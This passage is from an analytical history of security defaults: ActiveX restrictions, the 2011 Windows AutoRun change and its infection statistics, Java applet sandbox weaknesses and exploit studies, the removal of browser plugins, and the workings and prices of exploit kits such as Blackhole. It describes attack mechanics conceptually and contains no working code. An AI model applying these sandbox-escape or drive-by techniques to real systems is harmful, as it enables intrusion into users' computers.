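Microsoft responded in June 2010 by extending the check to controls that other controls load inside Office. Other programs remained exposed. Dewey and Traynor had proposed a single check for all of Windows. When their prototype applied the list to all of Internet Explorer, the browser lost its navigation bar, which depended on a blocked control, so Microsoft could not simply delete everything on the list.

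### Narrower defaults

The original default applied to downloads, but many controls came with Windows or other software and never triggered a download prompt. Dormann and Plakosh counted 2,701 components of this general type in a standard copy of Windows XP, of which 375 carried a safety label that let web pages use them.

Microsoft addressed these dormant controls in Internet Explorer 7 with ActiveX Opt-In. Cohen and Franco (2006) explain in *ActiveX Security* that the browser disabled installed controls by default on internet sites and asked the user before running one for the first time. Controls were exempt if the user had run them before upgrading or downloaded them through the new browser, or if they were on a pre-approved list. Developers added their own controls to that list with a registry entry, and in doing so certified that they knew of no vulnerability. Opt-In exposed fewer controls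 to each page, but left the remaining decisions to users and developers. In 2008 Dormann and Plakosh criticised Microsoft for leaving ActiveX enabled by default for internet sites and advised people to switch it off.

Microsoft then left ActiveX out of Edge, its successor to Internet Explorer, although Petri's *Office 2024 to Block ActiveX Controls by Default* notes that controls still work in Edge's Internet Explorer mode, which exists for old sites.

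Office documents could also contain controls, and the change came even later there. In September 2024 Microsoft (2024) announced that Office would stop asking users whether to enable controls and would default to a setting called "Disable all controls without notification". The change, which covers Word, Excel, PowerPoint and Visio, took effect in Office 2024 that October and began to reach Microsoft 365, the subscription version, in April 2025. Users can no longer create controls or interact with existing ones, some of which remain visible as static images, according to TechRepublic. Despite the setting's name, Microsoft's support page shows a message telling the user that Office has blocked ActiveX content in the file.

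### What ended it

Signatures, kill bits and Opt-In all restricted ActiveX, but Internet Explorer was still running it more than ten years after McLain's demonstration. The 2002 episode suggests that too many sites depended on it. Even one control could be too widely used to block, and removing the whole feature would have broken far more sites, including those of South Korean banks and public offices, which had built their services around it.

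Microsoft could leave ActiveX out of Edge because most of the web had stopped depending on it. Internet Explorer had lost its dominance to browsers that did not run ActiveX controls, and smartphones did not run them either, so a site that required one turned away a growing share of its visitors. This gave developers a commercial reason to replace their controls, whatever they thought about security. Dropping ActiveX was still a choice, and a safer one than keeping it, but if Internet Explorer had kept its market, Microsoft would probably have gone on adding prompts and kill bits.

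Microsoft's decision to turn ActiveX off by default in Office is better evidence of a choice made for security. Office had not lost its market as Internet Explorer had, and TechRadar's *ActiveX is now being blocked by default in Microsoft 365* (2025) reports that Microsoft gave security as the main reason, citing how much access a control has to the user's system. That access had been part of the design since 1996, and 28 years passed between Internet Exploder and the first Office release with controls off by default. Microsoft may have waited until few documents still used them. A user or administrator who needs a control can still turn ActiveX back on.

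## Windows AutoRun and the change of default in 2011

In 2011, thirteen years before it switched off ActiveX in Office by default, Microsoft changed the default for AutoRun, a Windows feature that started programs from discs and memory sticks. It made both changes for security reasons, and in this case it published figures on what happened afterwards.

### An instruction file on the disc

AutoRun arrived with Windows 95, when most software came on CDs. A publisher put a small text file called Autorun.inf on the disc, containing a line such as this:

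`open=setup.exe`

When a customer inserted the disc, Windows read its autorun.inf file and started the program listed there, so the customer did not have to find the installer. This was fairly safe on a factory-made CD, because nothing on the customer's computer could alter the contents, and people who insert a newly bought disc usually want to run what is on it.

AutoPlay is a different feature from AutoRun. Microsoft's *AutoRun changes in Windows 7* (2009) describes AutoPlay as the menu that lets a user choose what to do with an inserted disc or drive, such as play its music or view its photographs. AutoPlay also read Autorun.inf and added the task described there to the menu. A program on the disc or drive could therefore start by itself or appear as a menu choice, depending on the version of Windows and the kind of device.

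Any computer can write to a memory stick, so sticks lacked the protection that a factory-made disc had provided. A malicious program could copy itself onto a stick and add an Autorun.inf. According to *Microsoft Windows Does Not Disable AutoRun Properly*, a warning issued in January 2009 by US-CERT, the US government's computer emergency team, the program might then run when the user connected the stick to another computer, clicked its icon or picked an option from the AutoPlay menu. Windows could not determine whether the instructions came from the manufacturer, a person or malware. In *Improvements to AutoPlay*, a post for the Windows 7 engineering blog, Arik Cohen gave this as the reason for the later change.

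### Conficker, Taterf and Rimecud

The Conficker worm, which copied itself from one computer to the next, infected millions of PCs from late 2008. When someone plugged in an infected USB stick, the AutoPlay menu showed two entries that offered to open the folder and view the files. One came from Windows, and the other came from Conficker and started the worm. Cohen conceded that even a knowledgeable person who never ran untrusted software could easily choose the wrong one. An ActiveX prompt at least took the publisher's name from a certificate, but here the attacker wrote the text that the user had to rely on.

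Taterf and Rimecud, two other families of worms, also planted or altered Autorun.inf files on memory sticks and network drives (shared folders that Windows displays as disks). Holly Stewart (2011), in *Breaking up the Romance between Malware and Autorun*, gave Microsoft's detection counts for the last quarter of 2010: about 1.9 million for Rimecud, 1.7 million for Conficker and 1.6 million for Taterf. A general category for other malware that spread through AutoRun accounted for another 3.3 million. In June 2010, according to Threatpost's *AutoRun Infections Plummet Following Upgrade*, Samsung acknowledged that some of its phones sold in Germany had shipped with an AutoRun virus on the memory card.

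Few of these worms relied on AutoRun alone. Conficker also exploited a Windows flaw that Microsoft had patched in October 2008, and it tried a list of common passwords.

### Four stages, from registry to automatic update

At first, anyone who wanted AutoRun off had to edit the registry by hand, and even that did not fully work. US-CERT found that even with Microsoft's strictest setting, clicking a drive's icon could still run the program on it. US-CERT instead recommended pasting a line of text into Notepad, saving it as a registry file and double-clicking the file. In February, Microsoft (2009) issued a security advisory and automatically sent out a correction that made the setting work but left AutoRun on. The advisory listed a CVE number for the faulty setting but none for AutoRun itself.

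That same month Virus Bulletin (2009) argued that Microsoft should remove AutoRun and AutoPlay for writable media, at least for programs. In April Microsoft announced that Windows 7 would largely do so. AutoPlay would still offer to open a memory stick's files, but it would ignore any program specified on the stick. Christopher (2009), in *Changes in Windows to Meet Changes in Threat Landscape*, explained that abuse had increased so much since the start of the year that Microsoft had decided to shift the balance between security and convenience.

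Microsoft offered the same change for Windows XP and Vista on 25 August 2009, but only on its download site, so users had to know about it and fetch it. Automatic delivery began on 8 February 2011, but the update was still optional on XP, as a writer for the security firm F-Secure noticed on a test machine. *News of AutoRun's Death Has Been Greatly Exaggerated* (Sean, 2011) gives Microsoft's explanation as "a miscommunication and not a mistake". *Microsoft's Autorun update v2.1 now automatically deployed from Windows Update* (Mohan, 2011) reports that computers were installing it automatically by 2 March.

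Microsoft labelled the update "important, non-security". Adam Shostack (2011), in *Deeper insight into the Security Advisory 967940 update*, gave Microsoft's usual reason, which was that it did not count behaviour it had designed as a vulnerability. A security update was also supposed to fix every known variant of a problem, and this update left part of AutoRun running.

### The exception for optical discs

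CDs and DVDs kept AutoRun. Christopher argued that malware generally does not spread on media it cannot write to. But home users could write their own discs, and a reader commenting on Cohen's post in 2009 named three families of malware that hid in the folder where Windows collected files for burning, so that the next disc carried them. In 2011 Shostack said Microsoft had not seen malware exploiting discs in the wild, which conflicts with the reader's claim. Shostack also argued that an infection would spread slowly because people burned discs much less often than they plugged in memory sticks, and this holds whichever claim is right.

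Windows also treated some USB devices as discs because their built-in software identified them as CD drives. Datamation's *Securing Windows Autorun Autoplay Good Method vs Bad Method* gives the example of an LG phone that presented itself as a CD drive so that its owner could copy music easily. F-Secure tested a Western Digital hard disk with a virtual CD on board, and found that XP launched its installer without asking, while Windows 7 only offered to run it. An ordinary memory stick does not present itself this way, and a worm could not easily make it do so by copying files onto it.

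For other devices, the installation message disappeared. Readers of Cohen's post complained that non-technical owners of USB modems would struggle to find the right installer among several badly named files, and that programs carried on a stick would no longer start by themselves. One reader proposed that Windows check for signed code instead of ignoring the instruction file. That would have kept the convenience but brought in the weaknesses of the ActiveX trust model, and another reader objected that the certificates would cost small developers $200 to $500 a year. Microsoft instead provided a tool that let customers reverse the change.

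### The fall in infections

Microsoft measured the effect with its Malicious Software Removal Tool, a free program that Windows Update distributes every month. The tool scans for selected common malware families, removes what it finds and reports the result. It ran on more than 600 million computers a month and counted actual infections, whereas an antivirus program also counts the attempts it blocks.

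Microsoft's *Autorun-Related Malware Declines and the June 2011 Security Bulletin Release* (2011) reports that by May 2011 the infections found per scanned computer had fallen from their 2010 rates by 59 per cent on XP and 74 per cent on Vista. News reports added other comparisons from a companion post by Stewart. Computerworld's *Windows XP, Vista AutoRun update reduces malware infections by 82%* (2011) measured the change from January 2011 and gave separate figures for each service pack, Microsoft's term for a large cumulative update. Softpedia (2011) quoted the total number of infections avoided.

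| Measure | Compared with | Windows XP | Windows Vista |
|---|---|---|---|
| Infections found per scanned computer, May 2011 | 2010 rates | Down 59% | Down 74% |
| Infection rate by service pack, May 2011 | January 2011 | Down 62% (Service Pack 3) | Down 68% (Service Pack 1) and 82% (Service Pack 2) |
| Number of infections, February to May 2011 | The three months before the update | 1.3 million fewer on XP and Vista together | |

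The 1.3 million is a raw count for both systems, so it partly depends on how many people were still using them, a problem that rates per scanned computer avoid. The Register's *Malware abusing Windows Autorun plummets* reports from Microsoft's chart that infections fell from a peak of about 1.8 million in June 2010 to a little more than 400,000 in May 2011. Infections reached that peak even though Microsoft had offered the same update on its download site for ten months.

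### What else might explain it

None of these figures shows how any particular computer was infected. Shostack wrote of malware "that uses Autorun to propagate" because Microsoft did not know how many infections AutoRun had caused. According to Rashid (2011), in *Autorun Malware Declined Since Update*, Stewart acknowledged that some of these worms also spread through network shares, guessed passwords and old flaws. To estimate each route's share, Faulhaber, Lambert and colleagues (2011), in *Microsoft Security Intelligence Report Volume 11*, divided each family's infections equally among the methods it was known to use to spread. Conficker had four, so 100 Conficker infections counted as 25 each for the Windows flaw, passwords, AutoRun on removable drives and AutoRun on network drives. By this method, AutoRun accounted for 43 per cent of the infections they analysed from the first half of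 2011. The equal split is an assumption, and it gives AutoRun too much weight if most Conficker infections in companies came through passwords.

National clean-up campaigns may also have contributed. Microsoft (2009) credited cooperation between internet providers and government agencies in Japan and Germany with helping to keep infections low there, and Faulhaber and colleagues describe similar work in Korea, Poland and Portugal. Some worms were already declining before automatic delivery began. Detections of Taterf, for example, fell by about 31 per cent between the third and fourth quarters of 2010. Detections of Conficker and Rimecud rose over the same period, however, so AutoRun worms in general were not declining.

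Windows XP Service Pack 2, which Microsoft no longer supported, can serve as a comparison because it did not receive the update. Threatpost reported little change in infections on it, but a reader on the Tom's Hardware forum page *Windows Much Safer After Microsoft Killed Autorun* took Microsoft's chart to show a large fall, and suggested subtracting that fall from those on the updated versions. Even a large fall would be hard to interpret, because it might reflect a general decline in malware, or updated computers might have been infecting fewer memory sticks, so that fewer reached unprotected computers.

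Microsoft saw signs of that second effect on computers that already had its antivirus software. The software had been blocking the worms before February, yet attempts to infect these computers also dropped immediately after the release. Stewart compared this to the effect of second-hand smoke. *Windowsの自動実行機能 (Autorun) の無効化の効果について考える* (2011), a post by Microsoft's Japanese security team, reports that detections by the company's business antivirus product fell by about 80 per cent between February and May.

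Windows 7 offers separate evidence. In an average month of 2010, about 13 per cent of XP users with Microsoft's free antivirus program reported encountering one of these worms, against 9 per cent of Windows 7 users. Exposure was fairly similar, but XP users were nearly ten times as likely to be infected. Windows 7 also had other protections and ran on newer computers, and Stewart did not claim that AutoRun explained the whole gap.

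The update probably caused most of the fall in 2011. Clean-up campaigns and the slow replacement of old computers don't readily explain a drop that began with the release and appeared at once on protected and unprotected machines. The update's exact share is unknown because Microsoft's figures did not include a comparison of these worms with malware that had never used AutoRun.

### What the worms did next

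Attackers could also infect computers from memory sticks without AutoRun, through a flaw in Windows shortcuts, the small files that point to other files. Displaying a shortcut's icon was enough to make Windows load the malicious program. In mid-2010 researchers found that Stuxnet, the worm aimed at Iran's uranium enrichment programme, exploited this flaw. Faulhaber and colleagues report that several older malware families, many of which had used AutoRun, began exploiting it too, and that detections rose sharply in the second quarter of 2011.

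The timing is consistent with attackers moving from AutoRun to the shortcut flaw, but the first families had adopted the flaw before February 2011, so the update cannot fully explain the move. The rise also looks larger than it was because each affected computer reported the same attack eight times on average. Attackers gained less from the shortcut flaw than from AutoRun because it was an ordinary bug, which Microsoft had patched in August 2010. All exploits together made up about 6 per cent of the infections in the first half of 2011.

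The worms persisted. Conficker survived in company networks by guessing passwords such as "coffee" and "test", and Dark Reading's *Microsoft Conficker Worm Remains Ongoing Threat* reports that nearly 10 per cent of organisations had not installed the patch for the flaw Conficker exploited. *Old Malware Problem Resurfaces* (Poremba, 2012) noted that AutoRun malware was back in the news at the end of 2012.

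### A cheap change that came late

AutoRun on memory sticks was easy to give up because a user could still open the folder and double-click the installer, which took a few seconds. *Microsoft Windows Update Targets AutoRun Worms* (Prince, 2011) quotes Graham Cluley of the security firm Sophos, who thought that AutoRun had never been a necessary technology. Some of Cohen's readers disagreed, but they lost only convenience and could still use the data on their drives. Office macros were much harder to restrict because businesses had built their daily work on them, and Microsoft did not block them by default in files from the internet until 2022.

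Microsoft also controlled the only program that had to change, unlike with ActiveX on the web. Once Windows treated the instruction file differently, USB sticks already in circulation could no longer start a program automatically on an updated computer.

Yet worms and trojans had abused AutoRun for more than a decade by then, according to The Register, which asked Microsoft why it had waited so long. Jerry Bryant, a manager in Microsoft's security response team, said the industry had needed time to move to newer technology in Windows and that the company had waited until its partners agreed. This explains the 22 months between the announcement for Windows 7 and automatic delivery to XP and Vista. In that time, some makers of devices that needed programs to start automatically built the CD imitation into their products, so the exception for discs made the change easier for them to accept.

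AutoRun became more dangerous as memory sticks replaced discs, and Microsoft dated the sharp increase in abuse to the beginning of 2009. Microsoft's own rules also made it easy to delay changing the default, since they did not require a security update for a feature that worked as designed. Partners who depended on AutoRun could complain to Microsoft directly, while the harm was scattered among users who seldom knew how they had been infected. Stewart wrote that her team's analysis of infections was pivotal in the decision to change the default, so counting infections seems to have given Microsoft a reason to act that its security rules had not.

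## Java applets and the removal of browser plugins, 1995 to 2018

Microsoft could stop AutoRun on memory sticks by changing Windows, but Java applets, small programs that a web page ran inside the browser, depended on more than one company. Sun Microsystems, and later Oracle, supplied the software that ran them, while Netscape, Microsoft, Google and others made the browsers that loaded it. Sun and Oracle spent about twenty years repairing applet security, and the browser makers eventually removed support for applets.

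Sun released Java in mid-1995 as part of its own browser, HotJava, and Netscape soon announced that it would build Java into Navigator, then the leading browser. Applets could add animations or chat windows to pages that had held mostly text and pictures. Race (2025) recalls in *So Long and Thanks for All the Applets* that most uses of Java in those years centered on applets.

Sun let web pages run programs from strangers but restricted what those programs could do, whereas ActiveX relied on signatures. An applet could connect to the server it came from and display pages, but it was not supposed to access the user's files.

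### How the sandbox worked

Java's sandbox consisted of more than a dozen mechanisms that all had to work, according to *An In-Depth Study of More Than Ten Years of Java Exploitation* (Holzinger, Triller and colleagues, 2016). One of them checked an applet's compiled code for illegal operations, such as treating a number as a memory address, before the applet ran. If this check missed an illegal operation, the applet could tamper with the other mechanisms.

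Java programs consist of units called classes, and a component called a class loader brings each class into memory and records where it came from. Classes from Java's own library, which was already on the user's computer, received full rights, while classes from a web page received very few. Applets could not use parts of the library called restricted packages, because these contained tools that could switch off the protection.

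An applet could not call the operating system directly. It had to call a library function instead. Before opening a file or network connection, that function called the security manager, which allowed or refused the request.

The security manager also had to determine which code had started a request, because an applet could make one through several library functions. It did this by inspecting the call stack, the record of function calls that have not yet finished. *Understanding Java Stack Inspection* (Wallach and Felten, 1998) explains the method using only two kinds of code, system and untrusted. The inspection starts at the newest call and works back towards the oldest. If an applet calls a library function that displays documents, and that function calls another that opens files, the inspection passes both library functions, reaches the untrusted applet and denies the request. By 1998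 Netscape, Microsoft and Sun all used versions of this method.

The rule would have broken harmless functions if applied strictly. *Twenty years of Escaping the Java Sandbox* (Eauvidoum and disk noise, 2021) gives the example of a library function for network data that needs to know the type of processor. Reading the processor type requires a permission that an applet may lack. The library's developer can therefore mark that step as privileged, using a function called `doPrivileged`, so that the inspection doesn't look further back. In effect the developer vouches that the step is safe whoever asked for it, which is true only if the applet cannot influence what the step does.

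Applets, the Java class library and the security manager all ran inside one program, with no operating system barrier between them. Dean, Felten and Wallach (1996), in *Java Security*, noted that this design made Java faster and easier to embed in other software. But hundreds of library classes had full rights, so a bug in any of them could let an applet escape its restrictions.

### Trusted code as a confused deputy

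Reviewers can search code for uses of `doPrivileged`. The library also granted privileges in a way that was harder to spot. Some of its functions, called caller-sensitive, checked their immediate caller and skipped the full inspection if that caller belonged to the library.

*Hardening Java's Access Control by Abolishing Implicit Privilege Elevation*, by Holzinger, Hermann and colleagues, illustrates the danger with an invented example. One library function can open any file, and it skips the inspection when another library function calls it. At first its only caller reads a fixed settings file, which is safe. In a later release, a developer adds a convenience function that opens whatever file its caller names. An applet can now open any file through the convenience function, because the file-opening function checks only its immediate caller, which is trusted.

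The convenience function is a confused deputy, like the ActiveX control that deleted whatever file a web page named. The function's developer may never have known that the code had special rights that needed protecting. Parts of the real library had comments warning programmers not to reorganise the code, because even a harmless-looking change could break the security of the whole platform.

Java's developers had introduced these shortcuts because they were convenient and because inspecting the whole stack took time. Even a full inspection could miss the influence of untrusted code, as Fournet and Gordon describe in *Stack Inspection*, because it considers only the current series of nested calls. If trusted code acts on a result that an untrusted program returned earlier, that program is no longer on the stack.

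### The warnings of 1996 and the exploits that followed

In 1996, within a year of Java's release, Dean, Felten and Wallach of Princeton University found serious security holes in HotJava and Netscape Navigator 2.0. One hole let an applet break the rule that it could connect only to the server it came from. The browser looked up the network addresses of that server and the one the applet was trying to reach, then compared them. An attacker could supply the result of one lookup, so an applet running inside a company could reach machines that the company's firewall hid from the internet.

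Dean and colleagues also found that the security manager failed all three requirements of an established standard for access-control components, which must run at every access, resist tampering and be simple enough to verify. Programmers had to remember to call it, and if one forgot, Java granted access. An applet that exploited another flaw could change its data. Nobody could verify the security manager, because Java lacked a precise definition of what its programs meant. The browsers also kept no log from which an investigator could reconstruct an attack.

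They concluded that Java in its existing form "cannot easily be made secure", and that patching particular flaws would not stop more from appearing. They did not think Java was unusually bad, and guessed that the same scrutiny would find similar problems in rival systems. *Java Security* (Balfanz, Felten and colleagues, 1997) later reported significant flaws in a group of browsers including Internet Explorer.

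In 1998, Sun redesigned part of the system, replacing the all-or-nothing sandbox with separate permissions for separate actions. Gong, who led this work, looks back on it in *Java Security Architecture Revisited*. The new design was more flexible, but it left a large library with full rights inside the sandbox.

In a 2016 study, Holzinger, Triller and colleagues collected 87 publicly available exploits, which are programs that take advantage of a flaw. They tested each one, discarded those that did not work and merged duplicates, which left 61. Of these, 56 bypassed the sandbox completely. The researchers found nine causes shared among the exploits.

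| Weakness | What it gave an attacker | Exploits using it, of 61 |
|---|---|---|
| Restricted classes | Use of library tools meant to be off limits | 32 |
| Loading of arbitrary classes | Access to classes that Java should have refused to load | 31 |
| Definition of privileged classes | A way to bring in the attacker's own code with full rights | 31 |
| Reflection | Access to the private parts of other classes | 28 |
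| Confused deputies | Trusted code that passed on the attacker's calls | 22 |
| Caller-sensitive functions | Checks that looked only at the immediate caller | 22 |
| Method handles | A newer route to abilities like those of reflection | 21 |
| Serialization and type confusion | Objects in forbidden states, or objects that Java mistook for another kind | 9 |
| Privileged code execution | Trusted code that ran the attacker's choice of action with full rights | 7 |

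The numbers add up to more than 61 because most attacks combined several weaknesses. One notable combination was a confused deputy with a caller-sensitive function. Replacing a few of those functions would have stopped 22 of the 61 exploits. Only four exploits, all against IBM's version of Java, abused code whose developers had explicitly raised its privileges. Raising privileges explicitly therefore seems easier to get right than raising them implicitly, although the researchers call for more study before anyone relies on this finding.

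The recommended redesign would not have secured the sandbox by itself, because another 28 exploits each needed essentially one flaw, and those flaws were scattered across different components. Java's design kept producing similar bugs, and unrelated bugs kept appearing too.

The sample is also biased. Of the 87 exploits, 52 came from one research company, Security Explorations, which looked for flaws in order to report them. The percentages are therefore better evidence of how the sandbox could break than of which methods criminals preferred.

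Patches often fixed a single flaw without removing its cause. Holzinger and colleagues report that an exploit written for one update of Java 7 still worked, after minor changes, on a release of Java 8. IBM's version of Java had a similar case. When a patch blocked one step of an exploit, attackers could also substitute another flaw of the same kind and keep the rest.

The number of restricted packages also grew, from four in the first release of Java 7 to eight in a January 2013 update and 47 in a Java 8 release that was current in 2016. Microsoft's list of kill bits for ActiveX had grown in much the same way. The researchers thought the growth in restricted packages was dangerous because Java had to keep applets from ever obtaining a restricted class, and an applet that obtained one could usually use it without further checks.

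In 1996 the danger was that a developer would forget to call the security manager. By 2016 the problem was often that a developer had called a function that skipped the stack inspection. Either oversight led Java to grant access that it should have refused.

A root fix for the shortcuts existed. In their follow-up study, Holzinger and colleagues built a version of the library with almost all of them removed and found no measurable slowdown on a standard set of test programs. Adopting it would have required security specialists to review every new use of `doPrivileged`, and some old applications would have needed new permissions. Oracle was considering the proposal, but by then Chrome had stopped running applets.

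### January 2013

On 10 January 2013, the CERT Coordination Center warned of a flaw in Java 7, CVE-2013-0422, that attackers were already using. Its *Java 7 fails to restrict access to privileged code* (2013) explains that the attack combined two weaknesses. One gave an applet access to restricted classes, and the other let it use reflection to bypass the limits on replacing the security manager. The flaw affected Windows, Mac and Linux computers. Java 6 was not affected because one of the functions involved was new in Java 7.

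Users could get infected just by visiting a malicious page, or an honest page that an attacker had altered, which is called a drive-by download. US-CERT issued an alert the same day, which CISA now publishes as *Oracle Java 7 Security Manager Bypass Vulnerability*. In it, US-CERT predicted that researchers or attackers would probably find more flaws, and advised users to consider disabling Java in their browsers.

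Three days later, Oracle released a patch, Java 7 Update 11, more than sixteen years after the Princeton paper. Oracle gave both vulnerabilities covered by the patch the maximum severity score of 10. The update also raised Java's default security level from "Medium" to "High", so Java would always ask the user before running an unsigned applet.

CERT/CC told people to disable Java in the browser unless they absolutely needed it, "even after updating to 7u11", and kept that advice when it last revised its warning in June. Immunity, a security company, had reported that Oracle had fixed only one of the two weaknesses, and CERT/CC also thought further flaws were likely. Disabling Java would protect users from those flaws even if Immunity was wrong.

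Oracle's prompt left the decision to the user, as HotJava had done by asking for permission whenever an applet attempted something outside the user's settings. The Princeton researchers had expected HotJava users to switch off the security or click "Okay" without reading. Oracle's prompt also had a bug. CERT Coordination Center confirmed that if someone had disabled Java in the browser and later turned it back on, Internet Explorer on Windows 7 and Vista could run unsigned applets without asking, whatever the security level. People who had followed the official advice to disable Java and then needed an applet could end up with less protection than the settings showed.

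### Click-to-play and the end of NPAPI

By then browser makers had begun to act on their own. Most browsers loaded Java through NPAPI, the Netscape plugin interface of the 1990s. Under a policy called click-to-play, the browser runs a plugin only if the user clicks, so an attacker can no longer infect visitors through a hidden applet unless they click. Chrome already blocked Java by default when Google announced in September 2013 that it would drop NPAPI. Chromium Blog's *Saying Goodbye to Our Old Friend NPAPI* (2013) attributes many of the browser's hangs, crashes and security incidents to NPAPI, and adds that mobile devices did not support it. It also says that Mozilla, which makes Firefox, planned click-to-play for every plugin except the current version of Flash.

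Google first hoped to finish by the end of 2014, but people gave up plugins more slowly than it had expected, as VentureBeat reported. Schuh (2014), in *The Final Countdown for NPAPI*, set out the remaining steps:

1. In January 2015 Chrome would end the exemptions it had given to a few popular plugins, and block every NPAPI plugin unless the user allowed it for a particular site.
2. In April it would switch NPAPI off by default. Advanced users could turn it back on, and companies could do so for their employees through an administrator's policy.
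3. In September it would remove that override along with NPAPI itself.

Google based these dates on how many Chrome users had launched each plugin in a month.

| Plugin | Users who launched it, September 2013 | Users who launched it, October 2014 | Relative fall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google Earth | 9.1% | 0.1% | 99% |
| Unity | 9.1% | 1.9% | 79% |
| Java | 8.9% | 3.7% | 58% |
| Facebook Video | 6% | 3% | 50% |
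| Silverlight | 15% | 11% | 27% |
| Google Talk | 8.7% | 7% | 20% |

The share of Chrome users who ran Java in a given month fell by more than half in thirteen months. The blocking itself probably caused some of that fall, since users who ignored a blocked applet were not counted as launching Java. The figures also exclude people who used Internet Explorer at work, where old applets were more likely to matter. Still, even at the start, the share was below one in ten. Security Explorations (2016) cited 1.1 billion desktop computers with Java, so many of their owners must have been exposed to attacks through a plugin they hardly used.

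The override gave companies about five months to replace essential applets. The Chromium Blog also pointed them to Legacy Browser Support, which opened selected sites in another browser. For many, that was Internet Explorer, which loaded Java through ActiveX rather than NPAPI. Firefox stopped running Java by 2017, and Microsoft built Edge without ActiveX. Flash kept working in Chrome after the change because the built-in version used a different interface.

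Security was one of several reasons for removing NPAPI. Browser makers received the complaints when a plugin crashed, while the plugin's maker got most of the benefit from keeping it. The web already worked on phones without plugins, and newer web standards could do much of what plugins had done. Fewer of these reasons applied to Oracle, which was still supplying the Java plugin when Chrome stopped loading it.

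### Java without applets

Browser vendors were already acting against plugins when Oracle deprecated the applet interface in 2017, warning developers to stop using it, according to *JEP 504* (2024), a proposal from OpenJDK, the open-source project that develops Java. Java 11 ended browser plugin support in 2018, according to TFiR, a technology news site. Oracle marked the interface for removal in 2021 and removed it from Java 26, scheduled for March 2026.

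Few developers needed applets by then. Java's lasting use was on servers, where companies run programs they have chosen and installed themselves. Oracle had told those customers in its January 2013 alert that the two flaws did not affect them. Withdrawing applets therefore hurt Oracle far less than withdrawing Java would have.

Removing plugins from browsers did not repair the sandbox. Eauvidoum and disk noise found that some of the weaknesses identified at Princeton were still present in 2021. They note that researchers seem to have lost interest in the sandbox once it was no longer an easy way into people's computers, yet someone still published a complete escape in 2018. Oracle eventually gave up the sandbox too. According to OpenJDK's *JEP draft* (2024) for removing applets, an earlier proposal had "already effectively removed" the security manager, which some server operators had also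 used to keep applications apart.

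## Exploit kits and mass attacks through Java and Flash, 2006 to 2016

Many of the researchers who broke Java's sandbox did so to report the flaws. Criminals turned flaws of the same kind into a product called the exploit kit, a package of ready-made attacks on browsers and plugins that runs on a web server and attacks each visitor automatically. *Manufacturing Compromise* (Grier, Ballard and colleagues, 2012) traces the kits back at least to MPack in 2006. By 2011, the security firm Team Cymru (2011) had installed and compared more than 40 of them.

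### From a radio station's advert to an infected computer

To get visitors, an attacker could break into a legitimate website and add an invisible, zero-pixel frame that loaded a page from elsewhere, or could place an advertisement. *All Your iFRAMEs Point to Us* (Provos, Mavrommatis and colleagues, 2008) traces one chain of advertisements that began on a Dutch radio station's website. The station showed a banner from a German advertising company, whose script sent the browser to an American advertiser, which sent it on to a Dutch one. A second Dutch advertisement then loaded a disguised script from Austria, which sent the browser to a server that installed several malicious programs. The station had sold space to one company, but each resale let another party put content on its page.

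The kit at the end of such a chain checked the visitor's operating system, browser and plugins, then selected an attack to match. If the visitor had an unpatched version of Java or Flash, for example, the attack downloaded and started whatever program the kit's customer had chosen. The visitor saw no prompt, whereas ActiveX had at least shown one before installing a stranger's program.

### Division of labour and prices

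Few criminals did all of this themselves. Some wrote the kits, others found flaws for the kits to exploit, and others supplied visitors. The kits' customers provided the malware and made money from the infected computers.

Early kits sold for a single fee. Blackhole, which appeared in 2010, introduced rental. Its author supplied a server with the kit already installed and updated the attacks as Oracle and Adobe patched flaws. New plugin bugs kept appearing, so the author could replace attacks that no longer worked, and each patch gave customers a reason to keep paying. Some services sold infections, handling both the visitors and the attack. One of them, Traffbiz, paid website owners to add a small script that appeared to load a banner. The script sent visitors from Russia to a Blackhole server and showed everyone else an ordinary banner.

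Most of the known prices come from Grier and colleagues and from Krebs on Security (2016), a site that reports on cybercrime.

| What the buyer got | Price | Reported by |
|---|---|---|
| Phoenix kit, licence for one web domain | $400 in November 2009, later from $2,200 | Grier and colleagues |
| Blackhole server, one hour | $50 | Grier and colleagues |
| Blackhole server, one month | $500 | Grier and colleagues |
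| Blackhole kit, one month | $500 to $700 | Krebs on Security |
| Disguising a program from antivirus software, one month | $50 extra | Krebs on Security |
| Cool, a more exclusive kit from Blackhole's author, one month | $10,000 | Krebs on Security |
| A thousand visits, as paid to website owners | $0.80 to $3.00 | Grier and colleagues |

Screenshots of Blackhole's control panel showed attacks succeeding against 9 to 14 per cent of visitors. A customer who rented a server for a month at $500 and bought 100,000 visits at $3 a thousand would spend $800 and, at the lower success rate, infect 9,000 computers for about nine cents each. With the cheapest visits and the higher rate, the cost would fall to about four cents. Real customers probably paid more, because the visit prices are what a middleman paid his suppliers, but infecting a computer clearly cost little compared with what a stolen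 bank password could bring in.

### Two studies of drive-by downloads

Two of the four researchers in the 2008 study, including Provos, worked at Google, and the team could search the company's copy of the web. Software scanned about a billion pages a day for signs of tampering, such as frames in odd places, and passed about a million suspicious ones to a second stage. There, a clean copy of Windows opened each page in an unpatched version of Internet Explorer and waited about two minutes. The system labelled a page malicious only if new programs or changed files appeared on the computer and an antivirus scanner recognised something the page had sent.

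Between January and October 2007 the researchers checked 66.5 million addresses this way and found 3.4 million malicious ones, on about 182,000 sites. These addresses led to only 9,340 sites that distributed the malicious programs. The first stage had picked out suspicious pages, so the ratio of malicious to checked pages doesn't show how dangerous the web was. About 1.3 per cent of Google searches returned at least one malicious address, which is a better guide. Many people would not have clicked on that result, and many had a patched browser, so this figure measures exposure rather than infection.

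Careful browsing gave limited protection. Adult pages were riskier than others, but far more malicious pages covered ordinary subjects. Advertisements were the source of infection on only 2 per cent of the sites that led to it, but those sites were popular enough to make up 12 per cent of malicious search results. Many site owners had also failed to update their software, and 38 per cent of the servers running Apache, a widely used web server program, reported an outdated version with known flaws.

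Grier and colleagues studied the programs that such pages installed. In the spring of 2012 they gathered more than 10,000 of them, some from about 77,000 malicious addresses that Google supplied and the rest from servers running Blackhole and Phoenix. They ran a sample of them on isolated computers, grouped those that behaved alike and found at least 32 families. They also examined programs from other sources, including email attachments and pirated software. The attachments were mostly worms nearly nine years old, which their makers had long since stopped controlling. The best-known malware came from drive-by downloads and from services that sold access to infected computers.

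In Google's data, Blackhole accounted for 28 per cent of the hacked sites that led to an attack, and all the recognisable kits together accounted for 47 per cent. Almost all the rest led straight to a program file, so the researchers could not tell whether a kit had been involved, and their figures for kits may be too low.

The servers were hard to block because the addresses that hosted the kits lasted a median of only 2.5 hours. The hacked sites that sent visitors there had been active for a median of 44 days, which made them the better target for defenders. The busiest 1 per cent of these sites received more than 22,500 estimated lookups a day in a sample of internet traffic where google.com received about 87,000, though one American internet provider supplied three-quarters of that sample.

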